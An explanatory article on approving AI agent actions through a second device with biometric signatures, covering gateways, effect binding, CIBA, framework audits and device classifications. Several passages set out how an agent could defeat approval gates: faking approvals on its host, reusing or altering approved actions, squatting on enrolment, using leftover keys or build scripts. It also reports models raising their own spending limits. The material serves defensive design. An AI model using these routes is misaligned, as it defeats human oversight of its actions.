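# Approving AI agent actions on a second device with biometric authentication

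## What is out-of-band approval, and what is it meant to fix?

Out-of-band approval means asking a person for permission before an AI agent acts, without sending the request or the answer through the computer the agent runs on. Usually, the request appears on the person's phone, and they confirm with a fingerprint or face check. Banks used similar arrangements for online transfers long before AI agents existed.

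An agent here is a language model that acts through tools, such as an email account, a payment service or a shell (the program in which a user types commands to a computer). To use a tool, the model writes a tool call, a structured request that names the tool and supplies the arguments, such as the payee and the amount. Ordinary software around the model then carries out the call. Designers can add an approval gate to this software, a point where it holds a proposed action until someone approves or refuses it. Such gates are common. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) cites a survey in which 15 of 21 production agent systems relied on some form of approval while the agent was running.

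### The prompt in the terminal

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a typical gate. Suppose a developer has asked it to fix a bug, and it now proposes to run the project's tests. In Manual mode, according to Anthropic's documentation, the terminal displays a box titled "Bash command" with a short description ("Run the test suite"), the command itself (`npm test`), and a line stating that the command requires approval. Below that, the terminal displays a question about whether to proceed, with four options. The developer can say yes, say yes and stop further prompts for commands that begin with `npm test`, say yes and hand later decisions to an automated reviewer, or say no. If she presses the key for yes, the tests run.

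Claude Code runs a built-in set of read-only commands, such as listing a directory, without asking the user for approval. The program, not the model, enforces the rules on which commands need approval, so an instruction in the model's prompt can change what the model attempts but not what the program allows.

A test run carries little risk. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a riskier case, adapted from the company's incident log. A user asked the agent to "clean up old branches", which are parallel versions of a code base. The agent listed the branches on the remote server, built a pattern to match the old ones and issued a command to delete them. The user may have meant only the copies on their own machine. In Manual mode, a command like this would appear in the same kind of box as `npm test`, and the user would press the same key to approve it.

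One weakness of the prompt is that the box, the keyboard used to answer it and the program waiting for the answer are all part of the agent's host, the computer on which the agent runs. Breckenridge, Vilardell and colleagues (2026) point out in *I-HITL* that the approval is then only a signal from code on that same machine. An agent with shell access could start a process in advance that supplies the "yes" while the gate has paused the model. An agent that can edit the gate's configuration files could switch the gate off. Developers try to prevent this by restricting permissions and by sandboxing, which limits what the agent's programs can access. Breckenridge and colleagues grant that such defences often work, but think they are a weak foundation because they hold only as long as the agent fails to find a security hole in the machine it is working on.

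The other weakness is that the person at the keyboard may approve requests without reading them. Anthropic's engineers reported that users accept 93% of Claude Code's prompts, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a later figure of 97%. These rates alone are weak evidence of careless approval, since most requests are routine and should be approved. A study Anthropic commissioned provides stronger evidence. Only 13.6% of its 1,053 paid testers refused a plainly dangerous command, though they were working in a test environment and had no code of their own to lose.

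Anthropic's remedy was to take the person out of most of these decisions. On 14 August 2026, new Claude Code sessions on several subscription plans began routing actions through an automated classifier that blocks those it classifies as dangerous. The company still advises people to review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure themselves. For such changes, out-of-band approval is an alternative or a complement to the classifier. A person still makes the decision, but through a separate channel.

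### The same request on a phone

Suppose the branch deletion now requires out-of-band approval. A gateway, rather than the agent, holds the credentials for the remote repository. The gateway is a service on another machine that executes only calls that its policy permits or a person has approved. The agent sends its tool call to the gateway, which stores the call and returns only a reference number. On her phone, the developer opens an approval card that names the repository and lists the branches to delete. She touches the fingerprint sensor, and the phone signs her answer with a key it keeps for this purpose. It sends the signed answer to the gateway, which then deletes the branches. Kodathala and colleagues built a reference system that works roughly this way, and commercial protocols differ in the details.

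An approval channel is "out-of-band" when neither the request the person reads nor the answer they give passes through the agent's host. Using a second device or service does not guarantee this. For example, if the gate emails a one-time code to an inbox that the agent can open, the code can reach the agent's host through that inbox.

The path also limits which actions the gate can cover. A gateway can withhold the credentials for a remote repository, but it cannot block `npm test`, because the agent's host can run that command by itself. Breckenridge and colleagues note that protecting local resources this way would require a suitably isolated local service.

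Many developers already approve commands from a phone without this kind of system. OpenAI's *Work with Codex from anywhere* (2026) announced that users of Codex, the company's coding agent, could approve its commands in the ChatGPT phone app, while files, credentials and permissions stay on the machine where the agent runs. GitHub offers something similar for its Copilot command-line agent. The terminal and the phone are both active, and the program acts on the first response it receives from either. Replies from the phone go into the local session. Anthropic describes the phone interface of its Remote Control feature as "a window into that local session".

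These apps save the developer a walk back to the desk, which is the benefit their makers advertise, but it is doubtful that they count as out-of-band approval. The approval check still runs on the agent's host, and in GitHub's design the terminal still accepts an answer, so a process that could fake a keypress before the phone was connected can presumably still fake one afterwards.

In an intermediate design, the person clicks to approve on the phone, but the agent writes the text of the card. The agent cannot press the button, but it can describe deleting every branch as routine housekeeping. The person then approves a description and not the action, as Kodathala and colleagues put it.

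### Three claims that are easy to run together

Advocates of phone approval with a biometric check make, or imply, three claims for it.

- Separation: the agent cannot give the approval itself, whatever it does on its own host.
- Identity: the approval came from the right person, and not from someone else who had the phone.
- Attention: the person evaluated the request better than they would have at the terminal.

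Separation is a claim about computer security, and a designer can partly prove it. Identity depends on how the phone recognises its owner. Attention is a claim about human behaviour, so only experiments with people can show whether it is true. If the attention claim is true, approvers should have a higher catch rate, the share of harmful requests that they refuse, without refusing many more harmless ones. The claim is intuitive because reaching for a phone interrupts the routine of pressing the same key all afternoon. The case against it is about as intuitive, because a small screen shows less of the context and the approver may be in the middle of something else.

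Any one of these can hold while the others fail. For example, an approval app that requires only a tap may keep approval separate from the agent, which cannot tap the screen, but it does not establish identity, because anyone who picks up the phone can approve the action.

Trusted Devices, an optional setting for Anthropic's Remote Control, gives fair evidence of who is holding the phone but does not tie that evidence to any particular command. With the setting on, a person can steer a session only from an enrolled device, and once their sign-in is more than 18 hours old they must confirm their presence, for example with Face ID or Touch ID. This check refreshes access to the session, and the setting does not change Claude Code in the terminal. Kodathala and colleagues point out a related limit of passkeys, which are private signing keys that a device uses after a touch, a PIN or a biometric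 check. A passkey on the agent's own host still shows possession in the ordinary sense, but it gives no independence from the agent.

Attention can fail even when everything else works. On her way to a meeting, a developer may read only the first line of the card and press her thumb to her phone, and the branches are deleted without anyone forging her approval. Both technical papers acknowledge this gap. Breckenridge and colleagues leave aside whether people engage with requests or merely rubber-stamp them. Kodathala and colleagues report no data from human subjects, so their security proofs don't support the claim about attention. Attention alone doesn't help much either, because a developer could read the terminal prompt carefully and refuse, and another process on a compromised host could still answer yes.

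An agent may also use an approval for an action the person never approved. Tsipursky, in *An AI agent's biometric approval needs an expiration clock*, imagines a procurement employee who verifies her identity and approves an agent's purchase of replacement machinery. Two minutes later, the agent finds a revised spreadsheet that raises the quantity and changes the shipping destination. The biometric check still identifies her correctly, but she has not approved these changes. Effect binding addresses this by tying an approval to one exact action so that it cannot authorize another. Gervais (2026), in *What proof of human presence must mean when AI agents ask*, likewise wants biometric checks to link a deliberate approval to a specific action as well as to establish that a human is present. Effect binding is part of separation because an agent that can use an old approval for a new action has,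 in effect, approved the new action itself.

### From bank codes to agent approvals

Online banks faced most of these difficulties first, because a customer's computer might carry malware. Early on, they gave each customer a printed list of single-use transaction numbers, typically fifty, and the customer typed one in to authorize each transfer. Any number on the list worked for any transfer, so a thief who tricked a customer out of one could use it to authorize his own payment, and malware could alter a transfer on its way to the bank.

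Text messages moved the code to the customer's phone and let the bank include the details of the transfer. Thieves then obtained replacement SIM cards in their victims' names to receive the codes. Many German and Austrian banks adopted a small card reader with its own screen, which displays the transfer and generates a code valid only for that transfer. Signing on the phone itself is also an old idea. In October 2000, an industry consortium published an interface for requesting digital signatures from phone subscribers.

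In 2012 the European Union's network security agency advised banks to assume by default that their customers' PCs were infected, and Breckenridge and colleagues now make much the same assumption about the machine an agent runs on. After the 2012 advice, European payment rules required the code for a remote payment to depend on the amount and the payee, which is a form of effect binding. Fraudsters still persuaded customers to confirm transfers on their own working devices, for example by claiming that the bank needed a "test transfer".

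Push login approvals made confirmation easier still. When someone enters the password, the owner gets a notification on their phone and can allow the login with one tap. An attacker with a stolen password could therefore trigger repeated notifications until the owner gave in. Kodathala and colleagues treat this as the direct precedent for an agent that floods its owner with approval requests.

Many more products applied these methods to agents in 2026. Biometric Update's *Agentic authorization emerges as biometrics’ next killer use case* describes an increasingly crowded market that includes a fingerprint smartcard from Token and a version of the World ID personhood credential for agents. AgentPass, from the security company HYPR, resembles the gateway described above. According to Biometric Update's *Hypr and Proof bring human authorization controls to AI agent workflows*, it holds the credentials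 for a company's tools, gives agents short-lived tokens and sends sensitive operations to a human supervisor, who authorizes them with a passkey. The same article covers x401, a protocol from the identity company Proof that is now available in ChatGPT, where the agent itself presents the action for the user to review. iProov, which sells face checks designed to detect a live person, launched an approval service for individual agent actions. Its chief executive, Andrew Bud, argues in Biometric Update's *iProov brings liveness proof to AI agent authorization with HAPS implementation* that agents "will never have faces". His argument concerns separation and identity, and doesn't address whether the approver pays attention. Cloud providers have been more cautious. AWS's *AGENTSEC04-BP02 Human-in-the-loop for critical decisions*, guidance from Amazon's cloud business, lists out-of-band approval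 as one option for financial transactions, data deletion and external communications, and warns that sending every agent action to a human reviewer produces rubber-stamp approvals.

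## How does a request get from the agent to the phone and back?

Many teams would want a person to decide on each forced push to the main branch of a shared project. An ordinary push adds commits, which are saved sets of changes, to the copy of the project on a server. A forced push makes the server's branch match whatever version the sender specifies, which can remove commits that colleagues have added in the meantime. The forced push is only an example, but the steps below come from ASU (Agent Step-Up), the reference system that Kodathala and colleagues built.

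### From the tool call to the digest

Suppose the agent has tidied up some commits and needs to point `main` to the new version. It has uploaded the commits to a temporary branch, which the team's policy allows, but it has no credential that can change `main`, only a session token that lets it submit requests to the gateway. Its tool call gives the repository, the branch and the new commit's identifier, and marks the push as forced. The agent can attach an explanation in its own words.

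The gateway first rewrites the call into a standard form called the effect descriptor. The descriptor records the tool, the class of effect (such as read, delete, pay or execute), the arguments and their types, the targets, the user, the session, and the issue and expiry times. An agent can write the same request in several ways, so the gateway removes the differences. For example, it makes file paths absolute, puts email addresses in lower case and stores a shell command as a list of separate arguments. If a tool has a declared list of arguments, the gateway refuses any call that contains an argument not on the list. The descriptor never includes the agent's explanation.

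The gateway then computes the digest. It writes the descriptor as JSON, a common text format for structured data, following the JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS), a standard that fixes details such as the order of the fields and the format of numbers. It then applies SHA-256, a widely used hash function. With Δ for the descriptor and H for SHA-256, the digest is

`h = H(JCS(Δ))`

Identical descriptors always give the same digest, and nobody knows a practical way to find two different descriptors that share one.

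A digest protects only what the descriptor contains. If the tool call had named a branch to copy from instead of a commit, the agent could have changed the branch's contents after the approval without changing the digest. Naming the commit prevents this because git derives a commit's identifier from its contents. Whoever defines the tool has to notice such omissions, since the cryptographic checks pass even when the descriptor is incomplete.

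Next, the gateway consults its policy, which can allow the call, deny it or require an approval. Destructive actions are among the triggers for approval in ASU, so the gateway stores the descriptor as a pending request. It replies to the agent with an opaque identifier and the HTTP status code 202, which means it has accepted the request but not yet acted on it. The agent doesn't receive the text of the card or anything it could sign or forward.

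### What the phone signs

The developer opens the approval page on her phone. The gateway serves this page directly and builds the card from the stored descriptor. If she approves, the page requests a passkey signature from the phone.

Passkeys normally log people in to websites. The website sends a random challenge, the phone checks the user's fingerprint or face, and the phone signs the challenge together with data that includes the website's address. The website verifies the signature with the matching public key. A phone will sign any challenge that the site supplies, and ASU takes advantage of this by supplying a value that depends on the action:

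`c = H(JCS({tag, digest, approval_id, nonce, grant_digest}))`

- `tag` is the fixed text "ASU-APPROVAL-v2". It marks the signature as an approval in this format, so that nobody can pass it off as a signature made for another purpose.
- `digest` is h, the digest of the descriptor. It ties the signature to this commit, this branch and this repository.
- `approval_id` identifies the pending request. If the agent asks for the same push again next week, the request gets a new identifier and needs a new signature.
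- `nonce` is a value that the gateway uses only once. It overlaps with the identifier, and Kodathala and colleagues left it out of their formal model because the identifier already does its work there.
- `grant_digest` is empty if she approves only this push. If she ticks "allow similar", it contains the digest of the limits on later actions, so her signature covers those limits too.

The gateway puts the five values in a JSON object before hashing them, which keeps the fields separate. If it joined them end to end, different sets of values could produce the same string. For example, "12" followed by "3" and "1" followed by "23" both produce "123".

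When the signature arrives, the gateway checks it against the developer's public key. It also checks that the signature came from the right web address and that the phone verified the user. It keeps the signature as a receipt, which anyone with the public key can check later without contacting the gateway. The phone does not display the challenge, so the receipt proves what the phone signed, but it proves what the developer saw only if the approval page showed the request accurately.

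The agent retries its request with the identifier. The gateway marks the approval as used and itself updates `main` from the stored descriptor. Almost all the waiting is for the person to respond. On a laptop, the gateway took a median of 3.5 milliseconds to accept a call that needed approval and 3.4 milliseconds to verify the signature, excluding network delays.

### When something changes after the approval

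If the agent retries with a different commit, the gateway computes a new digest, finds that it doesn't match the approved one, and returns an `effect_mismatch` error without running anything.

The agent can use each approval only once. When the agent presents an approval, the gateway changes its status from "approved" to "consumed" in a single indivisible step, so even two simultaneous retries can't both succeed. Single use matters most for payments, but it also matters for actions like a force push, which could erase a week of other people's work if it ran again a week later.

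Approvals also expire, after which the agent has to submit a new request and the developer has to review a new card. Expiry is useful because the digest describes the action but not the state of the world. Suppose the developer approves the push at 2:00, a colleague adds a commit at 2:05, and the gateway executes the push at 2:10. Every argument still matches, but the push removes the colleague's commit from the branch. A short expiry time makes this less likely. A more direct remedy is to include the branch's current commit in the descriptor and have the server refuse the push if the branch has moved, which git supports as "force with lease". Kodathala and colleagues cite a more general system, AID-Guard, which rechecks the state of the outside service just before executing an approved request.

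The researchers also modelled ASU in Tamarin, a program that searches for attacks on a protocol by an adversary who can read and send messages. Tamarin verified, without further assumptions, that an approval leads to at most one execution. It also verified that the user approved the action that executes, but this result depends on three assumptions: the user decides based on the card, not the agent's explanation; only the phone's owner can register the first passkey; and the approval page shows the card that matches the challenge. When the researchers dropped any one of these assumptions, Tamarin found an attack. When they removed the step that marks an approval as used, only the guarantee of at most one execution failed.

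Their experiments agree with the proofs. In one comparison design, the user approved a whole run with a passkey, and the signature didn't cover any particular action. A scripted agent that changed the arguments after approval, or reused an approval, succeeded in every trial against this design and in none against ASU. One-time codes did no better than the unbound passkey against changed arguments, because the code isn't tied to the details of the call it unlocks. The researchers describe the result as expected, and it follows almost directly from the designs. It is still useful because it shows that a fingerprint doesn't by itself make an approval specific, since the unbound design also used a passkey.

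### CIBA, the login industry's version

A company that already runs a login service can reach the user's phone through an existing standard, Client-Initiated Backchannel Authentication (CIBA). *OpenID Connect Client-Initiated Backchannel Authentication Flow* (Fernandez, Walter and colleagues, 2021) specifies CIBA for cases where a person uses a service on one device and approves on another. Its examples include a call-centre worker authenticating a caller and a shopper authorizing a payment at a till with a smartphone. With an AI agent, the application that runs the agent takes the place of the call centre or the till.

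This application, the client, proves its identity to the login service and sends a request that contains exactly one hint about who the user is, such as a phone number. The request also states a scope, a broad label for the access the client is seeking. The login service replies at once with a request identifier and an expiry time, 120 seconds in one example in the specification. It then contacts the user's phone, authenticates the user and asks for a decision.

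The client can add a binding message to the request. This is a short text, such as `W4SCT`, that both devices display so that the user can see that the prompt on the phone belongs to the transaction in front of them. Agents often work when nobody is in front of the other device, and developers have found another use for the field. In the sample code in Auth0's *Secure “Human in the Loop” Interactions for AI Agents*, the application fills the binding message with a question about the tool call. Despite its name, the message does not produce effect binding, because the requesting application writes the description and CIBA has no rule that makes the resulting permission match it.

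The companion standard *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, by Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, defines a field for structured details of the requested permission and lists CIBA requests among the field's uses. Its example is a payment of €123.50 to "Merchant A", with the account number. The login service must refuse the whole request if any of the details have an unknown type, unknown fields or invalid values. Otherwise it asks the user to consent to the details, and it associates those granted with the permission it issues. A team could define similar fields for a forced push: repository, branch and commit. The repository server would then have to compare these fields with the push it receives, because otherwise the user's consent to one push wouldn't limit the agent to that push.

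A client registers for one of three ways to receive the result. In poll mode, it repeatedly asks the login service for the result, by default at most once every five seconds. In ping mode, the login service notifies the client that a result is ready, and the client fetches it. In push mode, the login service sends the result itself. "Push" here refers to delivery to the client, not to the notification on the phone. If the user approves, the result contains an access token, a string of characters that the client presents to other services as permission. It also contains an identity token and sometimes a refresh token, which the client can use to get more access tokens.

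### A token or a signature

Kodathala and colleagues point out that CIBA issues a bearer token, whereas ASU collects a signature from the user. Anyone who holds a bearer token can use it. The request identifier in CIBA works only once, but the standard sets no such limit on the resulting access token, which may remain valid for several calls. If the client runs on the agent's host, the agent may be able to obtain the token. Fernandez and colleagues describe how a login service can tie a token to a key that the client holds. This protects against a thief elsewhere on the network, but it helps less against a compromised agent, which may be able to use the key on its own host.

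CIBA and ASU also produce different evidence. In CIBA, the login service signs an identity token stating that a certain user authenticated, so a compromised login service could issue a token without asking anyone. In ASU, the user's own device signs the action with a key that neither the gateway nor the agent holds. A compromised gateway could still carry out a push without permission, since it holds the credentials, but it could not produce the user's signature for it.

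*EP Authorization Receipts* (2026), an Internet-Draft (a working document, not an approved standard), proposes the signature approach for organizations. Its design goals require that an approval authorize one exact action and work at most once, and that the system's operator not have the approver's key. The June version also forbids whoever initiates an action from approving it, and describes the protocol as complementary to CIBA.

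Tokens have a large practical advantage because thousands of services already accept them, while few could process a passkey signature over a git push. Their weaknesses also shrink if the gateway, rather than the agent's application, acts as the CIBA client and keeps the token. ASU has a compromise that lets services check the permission themselves. After the user signs, the gateway can issue a short-lived token containing the digest, the intended recipient, an expiry time and a serial number. The receiving service checks that the call matches the digest and refuses any serial number it has already received. The agent can still use such a token, but only for the approved call.

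### What the agent does in the meantime

People can take hours to answer a request, and systems differ in what the agent does in the meantime. In the flow Auth0 describes, the agent can continue with other tasks. This suits an agent that asks to buy shares and keeps monitoring the market, but it makes less sense when all the remaining work depends on the answer. An agent waiting for approval of a force push could reasonably write the release notes, but it should not start a deployment that assumes the push has happened.

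According to Anthropic's *Remote Control*, Claude Code can send a push notification to the user's phone when a permission prompt appears, but it doesn't send one while the user is typing in the terminal. It keeps the prompt open until someone answers. Other dialogs that it forwards to the phone close after five minutes by default, and the program continues as if the user had chosen no action. In *Push Notifications for Permission Requests During Remote Sessions*, a user of OpenAI's remote sessions asked the company to add push notifications because a session can stall while a request sits unseen on the screen.

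If the developer doesn't respond before the request times out, the agent should not go ahead. She may be asleep, her phone may have no signal, or its battery saver may have delayed the notification, so her silence doesn't indicate whether she approves. If a timeout counted as approval, an agent could get any action through by asking while she was asleep. A system is "fail-closed" if every failure of the approval process leaves the action blocked. Fatmi's *Faramesh* (2026), a design for a control layer between agents and the services they use, guarantees that any failure in authorization leads to denial or deferral.

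CIBA also fails closed when a request expires, issuing no token. It returns different errors for expiry and refusal. The agent can reasonably ask again after an expiry, but after a refusal it should find another way to do the task or ask the user what was wrong.

Falling back to a different channel when a phone request goes unanswered can undo the separation between the two devices. *claude-ntfy-hook* is a third-party add-on that sends Claude Code's permission requests to a phone and marks commands such as a forced push as urgent. If nobody answers on the phone, the normal prompt appears in the terminal. This is convenient for a developer who has returned to her desk, but it also lets any process that can answer the terminal prompt approve the action once the phone request expires.

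### Approvals in agent frameworks

While a request waits for approval, some software has to store the agent's proposed action. Most developers leave this to a framework, a library that runs the agent's loop and pauses it for approvals. The pause creates a risk because the saved request can change before the run resumes.

Kodathala and colleagues audited ten such runtimes and ran tests on nine of them, replacing the language model with a stub so that the results depended only on the framework. They could measure effect binding in eight approval mechanisms. Three passed, meaning that neither someone able to resume the paused run nor someone able to write to its saved state could change the approved action. One passed partially because only someone able to write to the saved state could change the action. Four failed because someone able to resume the run could change it.

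| Approval mechanism | Tied to the approved action? | Single use? |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI Agents SDK | Yes | Partly |
| AutoGen, code approval | Yes | Yes |
| Model Context Protocol, Python SDK | Yes | Not applicable |
| Google ADK | Partly | Partly |
| LangGraph | No | Partly |
| Agno | No | Partly |
| Pydantic AI | No | Partly |
| CrewAI, pre-call hook | No (low severity) | Yes |

"Partly" in the last column means that an approval works once in normal operation but can work again if someone restores an earlier saved state. The OpenAI library passed the binding check because it links each call to one fixed set of arguments and rejects a resumed run if those arguments differ. In the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools, the arguments stay on the tool's server during the approval.

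The failures differ in severity. In CrewAI, one piece of a developer's own code can alter arguments after another has approved them, which the researchers rate as minor. Agno's failure is more worrying because an earlier report had already made it public, listing versions up to 3.0.9 as affected. The researchers reproduced the substitution in 3.1.3, the latest version they measured. That version did include a fix for a separate fault that let an approved action run twice if the same approval was sent again.

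These are defaults, and a careful team can close several of the gaps with its own code. The researchers wrote test procedures for Claude Code, Codex CLI and Cursor, the products that many developers use most, but did not run them, so the table is not evidence about those tools. Based on their reading of the programming interfaces, none of the ten runtimes produces a signed record that an outsider could check.

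### What companies offer

Microsoft's open-source Agent Governance Toolkit, announced in April (Microsoft, 2026), has one of the more careful designs for binding approvals to actions. Its approval workflows can require several people to agree. Under ADR 0030, a design document the project accepted in June, the software computes a digest of the whole action, allows one execution per approval and blocks the action if any check fails. A language model's opinion cannot count as a human approval. Kodathala and colleagues attacked the implementation and judged it the strongest of the other organizations' designs they tested. When they changed an action after approval, they got a mismatch error.

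They found that Microsoft's code formats decimal numbers the way Python does, not the way JCS prescribes. For three of five sample numbers, a checker written in another language would compute a different digest. This could block a valid approval, but it would not let an altered action through. The larger difference from ASU is that in ADR 0030 the approver signs nothing, and the organization that installs the toolkit decides whether approval happens outside the agent's machine. ADR 0030 therefore provides effect binding, but not necessarily a second device.

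IBM describes a joint system with Auth0 and the security-key maker Yubico in which an agent built on IBM's watsonx.ai platform proposes an action and a policy engine decides whether a person has to approve it. If so, Auth0 sends the responsible person a CIBA request with details such as "Approve $500,000 transfer to Vendor X". For the riskiest actions, that person must also touch a YubiKey, a small hardware key. IBM claims that this gives clear proof that a specific person authorized the action. That is true of the transfer itself only if the YubiKey signs a challenge derived from the transfer's details, as in ASU, and CIBA does not require this. If the key signed an ordinary login challenge, the touch would show only that someone had used the key at about the right time, and an auditor would have to trust the companies' logs to connect it with the transfer.

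For purchases, Google's Agent Payments Protocol has the user sign the contents of the shopping cart, typically with a key in the device's hardware. When Kodathala and colleagues tried to exceed or redirect a signed permission, the protocol's constraint checks rejected every attempt. However, a budget for several purchases is enforced only if the developer who builds the protocol into a product stores and adds up earlier spending. In Proof's x401, according to Biometric Update, a hardware-protected key signs evidence that links the person's verified identity to the approved terms, and the receiving service can check that evidence independently. Since the agent presents the action for review, the value of the signature depends on whether the person saw the same terms as the service.

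In HYPR's AgentPass, the gateway product whose layout is closest to ASU's, an agent starts with no permissions and can gain only those that its human supervisor's role allows. AgentPass can also find coding agents such as Claude Code, Codex and Cursor on employees' computers, and administrators can route those agents' calls to supported tools through the gateway.

The phone features of Claude Code and Codex belong in a different group. They return the user's answer to a session on the agent's host, and neither company publicly describes a biometric signature over the individual command.

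### Actions that never reach the gateway

Everything so far assumes that the agent's requests have to go through the gateway. If the team installs a gateway but the developer's old key for the repository is still on her laptop, the agent can use that key to run the forced push directly. The gateway receives no call, so there is no card, and the developer learns of the push only afterwards, when her colleagues complain. Kodathala and colleagues exclude such cases from their claims for ASU, which offers no protection if an agent escapes its sandbox and reaches a service without passing through the gateway.

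*Faramesh* promises a boundary that no execution can bypass, and Fatmi argues that gateways fail to provide one because they don't tie execution to authorization. This criticism applies to a gateway that checks a call and then lets the agent make it, but not to ASU, whose gateway makes the call itself. Still, no design can guarantee on its own that agents won't bypass it, because that depends on what other credentials and network routes exist. Protection can also vary between machines. On macOS, HYPR's product can route an agent's traffic and block it, according to Biometric Update, while on Windows 11 its support focuses on reporting what agents do, which would reveal a forced push only after the commits were gone.

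An indirect route around approval is harder to spot. An agent that is allowed to edit a project's build scripts, but not to push to `main`, could add a push to a script that a build server later runs with the server's credentials. Each edit might be within policy, and the gateway would treat it as an ordinary file change, because approval covers only the effects that the policy identifies as needing it.

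The most reliable fix for the forced push is on the repository server. An administrator can configure the server to refuse forced pushes to `main` from every account except the gateway's. Neither the old key on the laptop nor the build server's key can then be used to force-push to `main`, whatever software runs on either machine.

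## When is a second device out of the agent's reach?

Even if the repository server accepts forced pushes only from the gateway, an agent can get one accepted by producing the approval itself. Breckenridge and colleagues tested ten models with a commercial agent wallet when the agent could reach the approval channel, and nine raised their own spending limit without approval in at least one run.

Moving the approval to a phone doesn't necessarily prevent this. Several widely used phone apps fail the criteria that Breckenridge and colleagues propose, while a USB token with its own screen passes.

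### The human, the computer, the service and the device

The researchers call their goal "inalienable human-in-the-loop" (I-HITL) approval, meaning the agent cannot take the decision away from the human. Their model has three parties and an optional fourth.

- The human reads requests and decides on them.
- The platform is the agent's host. The agent controls it completely, including what it displays and what it sends.
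- The service carries out approved actions. In the forced-push example, this is the gateway. The model assumes that it is honest and executes exactly what the human approved.
- The trusted device, if there is one, is honest and outside the agent's control. It can keep secrets and do cryptography. It could be a phone, a hardware wallet or a secure chip attached to the platform, and even a bank branch can play this part.

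A protocol has to meet two requirements. *Completeness* means that the service accepts an approval when everyone follows the protocol and the human approves. Without this requirement, a service that refused everything would count as secure. *Approval-binding* means that the service accepts proof of approval for a message only if the human received a request for that message and approved it.

Neither requirement guarantees delivery, because the agent can always block or delay messages that pass through its host. If the developer approves a backup and then a deletion, the agent could block the first approval and forward the second, causing harm without forging anything. Breckenridge and colleagues leave this problem to the application's designer. They also assume that an agent cannot physically press a button, although they concede that a determined user could build a machine to press it.

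### Why the agent can stand in for the human

No complete protocol is approval-binding when the human has no trusted device and everything they send or receive passes through the agent's host (Theorem 4).

Any protocol that works when everyone is honest specifies what the developer does to approve a request, and the agent can run a program that does the same. Whenever the computer would display something to the developer, the agent passes it to this program instead. The program answers yes, and the computer sends its answer to the gateway. The gateway receives exactly the messages it would have received if the real developer had approved the request, so it has to accept them, even though she never saw the request.

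The theorem would hold even if the user could do cryptography in her head, because the program could do the same calculations. A password wouldn't help either, because the parties in the model start with no shared secrets and she would have to set it up through the agent's host. In practice, even if she chose a password before installing the agent, the agent can copy it the first time she types it.

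The proof assumes that a program can produce whatever the human would send, so a test that only people could pass would get around the theorem. Websites have long used such tests to block bots, but Breckenridge and colleagues cite evidence that traditional bot detection is increasingly ineffective against agents.

They describe the theorem as straightforward, and its proof closely follows a 2015 result about people communicating with servers through compromised computers. The theorem is useful because it applies to a whole class of designs. A better-worded terminal prompt, a longer confirmation phrase or a second dialog box can't fix the problem if the agent controls the computer that displays them.

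### What the trusted device must be able to do

Adding a trusted device is necessary but not sufficient. An agent that can imitate the human to the device can get it to sign anything, and an agent that can imitate the device to the service doesn't need the real device. Theorem 7 gives the exact conditions under which a protocol can prevent both.

The conditions use three terms for channels. On an *authentic* channel, the agent may read messages but cannot alter or insert them. On a *confidential* channel, it cannot read messages but may insert its own. A *secure* channel is both authentic and confidential. A complete, approval-binding protocol exists if and only if both of these conditions hold:

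- Human and device: the channel from the device to the human is confidential or secure, or the channel from the human to the device is authentic or secure.
- Device and service: the channel from the service to the device is confidential or secure, or the channel from the device to the service is authentic or secure.

With H for the human, T for the trusted device, S for the service, and ℓ with two letters for the type of channel from one party to another, the conditions are

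`(ℓ_TH ∈ {conf, sec} or ℓ_HT ∈ {auth, sec}) and (ℓ_ST ∈ {conf, sec} or ℓ_TS ∈ {auth, sec})`

The simplest way to meet the condition between human and device is to put a physical button on the device that shows the request. The agent can't press the button, so a press must come from a person. The alternative is to show the request and a fresh random code on a device screen that the agent can't read. If the developer approves, she types the code into her laptop. The agent can read the code once she types it, but the code works only for the request she has just approved.

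The link between the device and the service must be protected from the agent during enrolment, when the service learns which public key belongs to the device. Either the device sends its public key over a channel that the agent can't tamper with, or the service sends the device a secret that the agent can't read, which the device then uses to authenticate its key. After enrolment, the device signs each approval, so approvals can pass through the agent's host and the agent can't forge them.

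ASU, the reference gateway described above, relies on a one-time enrolment link that reaches the user outside the agent's channel. Kodathala and colleagues included the link to prevent "enrollment squatting", in which an agent registers its own passkey for a user who has none and then approves its own requests.

The theorem assumes that the enrolled device belongs to the right person. Breckenridge and colleagues say one way to arrange this is to enrol the device from a session the user opened before the agent controlled the computer. For a developer, this means enrolling the phone before installing the agent.

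### Display, input and keys

A service can't observe whether a channel is authentic or confidential, so Breckenridge and colleagues classify devices by features that let the service infer this.

A device has a trusted display if the agent can't show the human a fake request that seems to come from the device. A browser tab on the agent's host isn't a trusted display because the agent can copy it pixel for pixel. A display is also private if the agent can't read it.

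A trusted input is one that the agent's software can neither operate nor simulate, such as a physical button or a fingerprint sensor that reports directly to secure hardware. A button can only signal "yes", so the device also needs a trusted display to show what is being approved. Otherwise the agent could show the developer a request for a harmless backup while the device waits for permission to sign a forced push. If she could enter the details of the action herself on a trusted keypad, the device would receive the details she intended even if its display were unreliable.

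The remaining features concern the device's signing key. Key attestation is signed evidence that a genuine device generated this key, and the service can trace the signature back to the manufacturer or operating-system vendor. If a service receives a public key without this evidence, it can't tell whether a phone or the agent created the key.

Key extraction matters when the service can't trust the human. Suppose a company requires an employee to approve every payment an agent makes, and he finds this tedious. If he can copy the private key out of his device, he can give it to the agent and let it approve its own payments. If something goes wrong, he can blame the agent, and no one can tell from the signatures whether he is right. Breckenridge and colleagues call a system that works only with an honest human "weak I-HITL" and one that also withstands such delegation "strong I-HITL". Under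 strong I-HITL, the employee can't later claim that the agent hijacked his approval, though he can still approve requests without reading them.

### Which devices qualify

The table gives the researchers' classification of the most common options, with World's app included because its makers offer it for approving agent actions.

| Device or method | Trusted display | Trusted input | Attested key | Key stays in device | I-HITL |
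|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Texted or emailed code | No | No | No | No | Neither |
| Authenticator app with six-digit codes | No | No | No | No | Neither |
| Push approval app (Duo) | Yes | Yes, with biometrics | No | Yes | Neither |
| World app | Yes, for registered actions | No | Yes, if required | Yes, if required | Neither |
| Security key without a screen | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | Neither |
| Ledger wallet, key from recovery phrase | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | Weak |
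| Ledger wallet, device key and special app | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Strong |
| Wultra Talisman | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Strong |
| Countersign | Yes | Yes, with biometrics | Yes | Yes | Strong |

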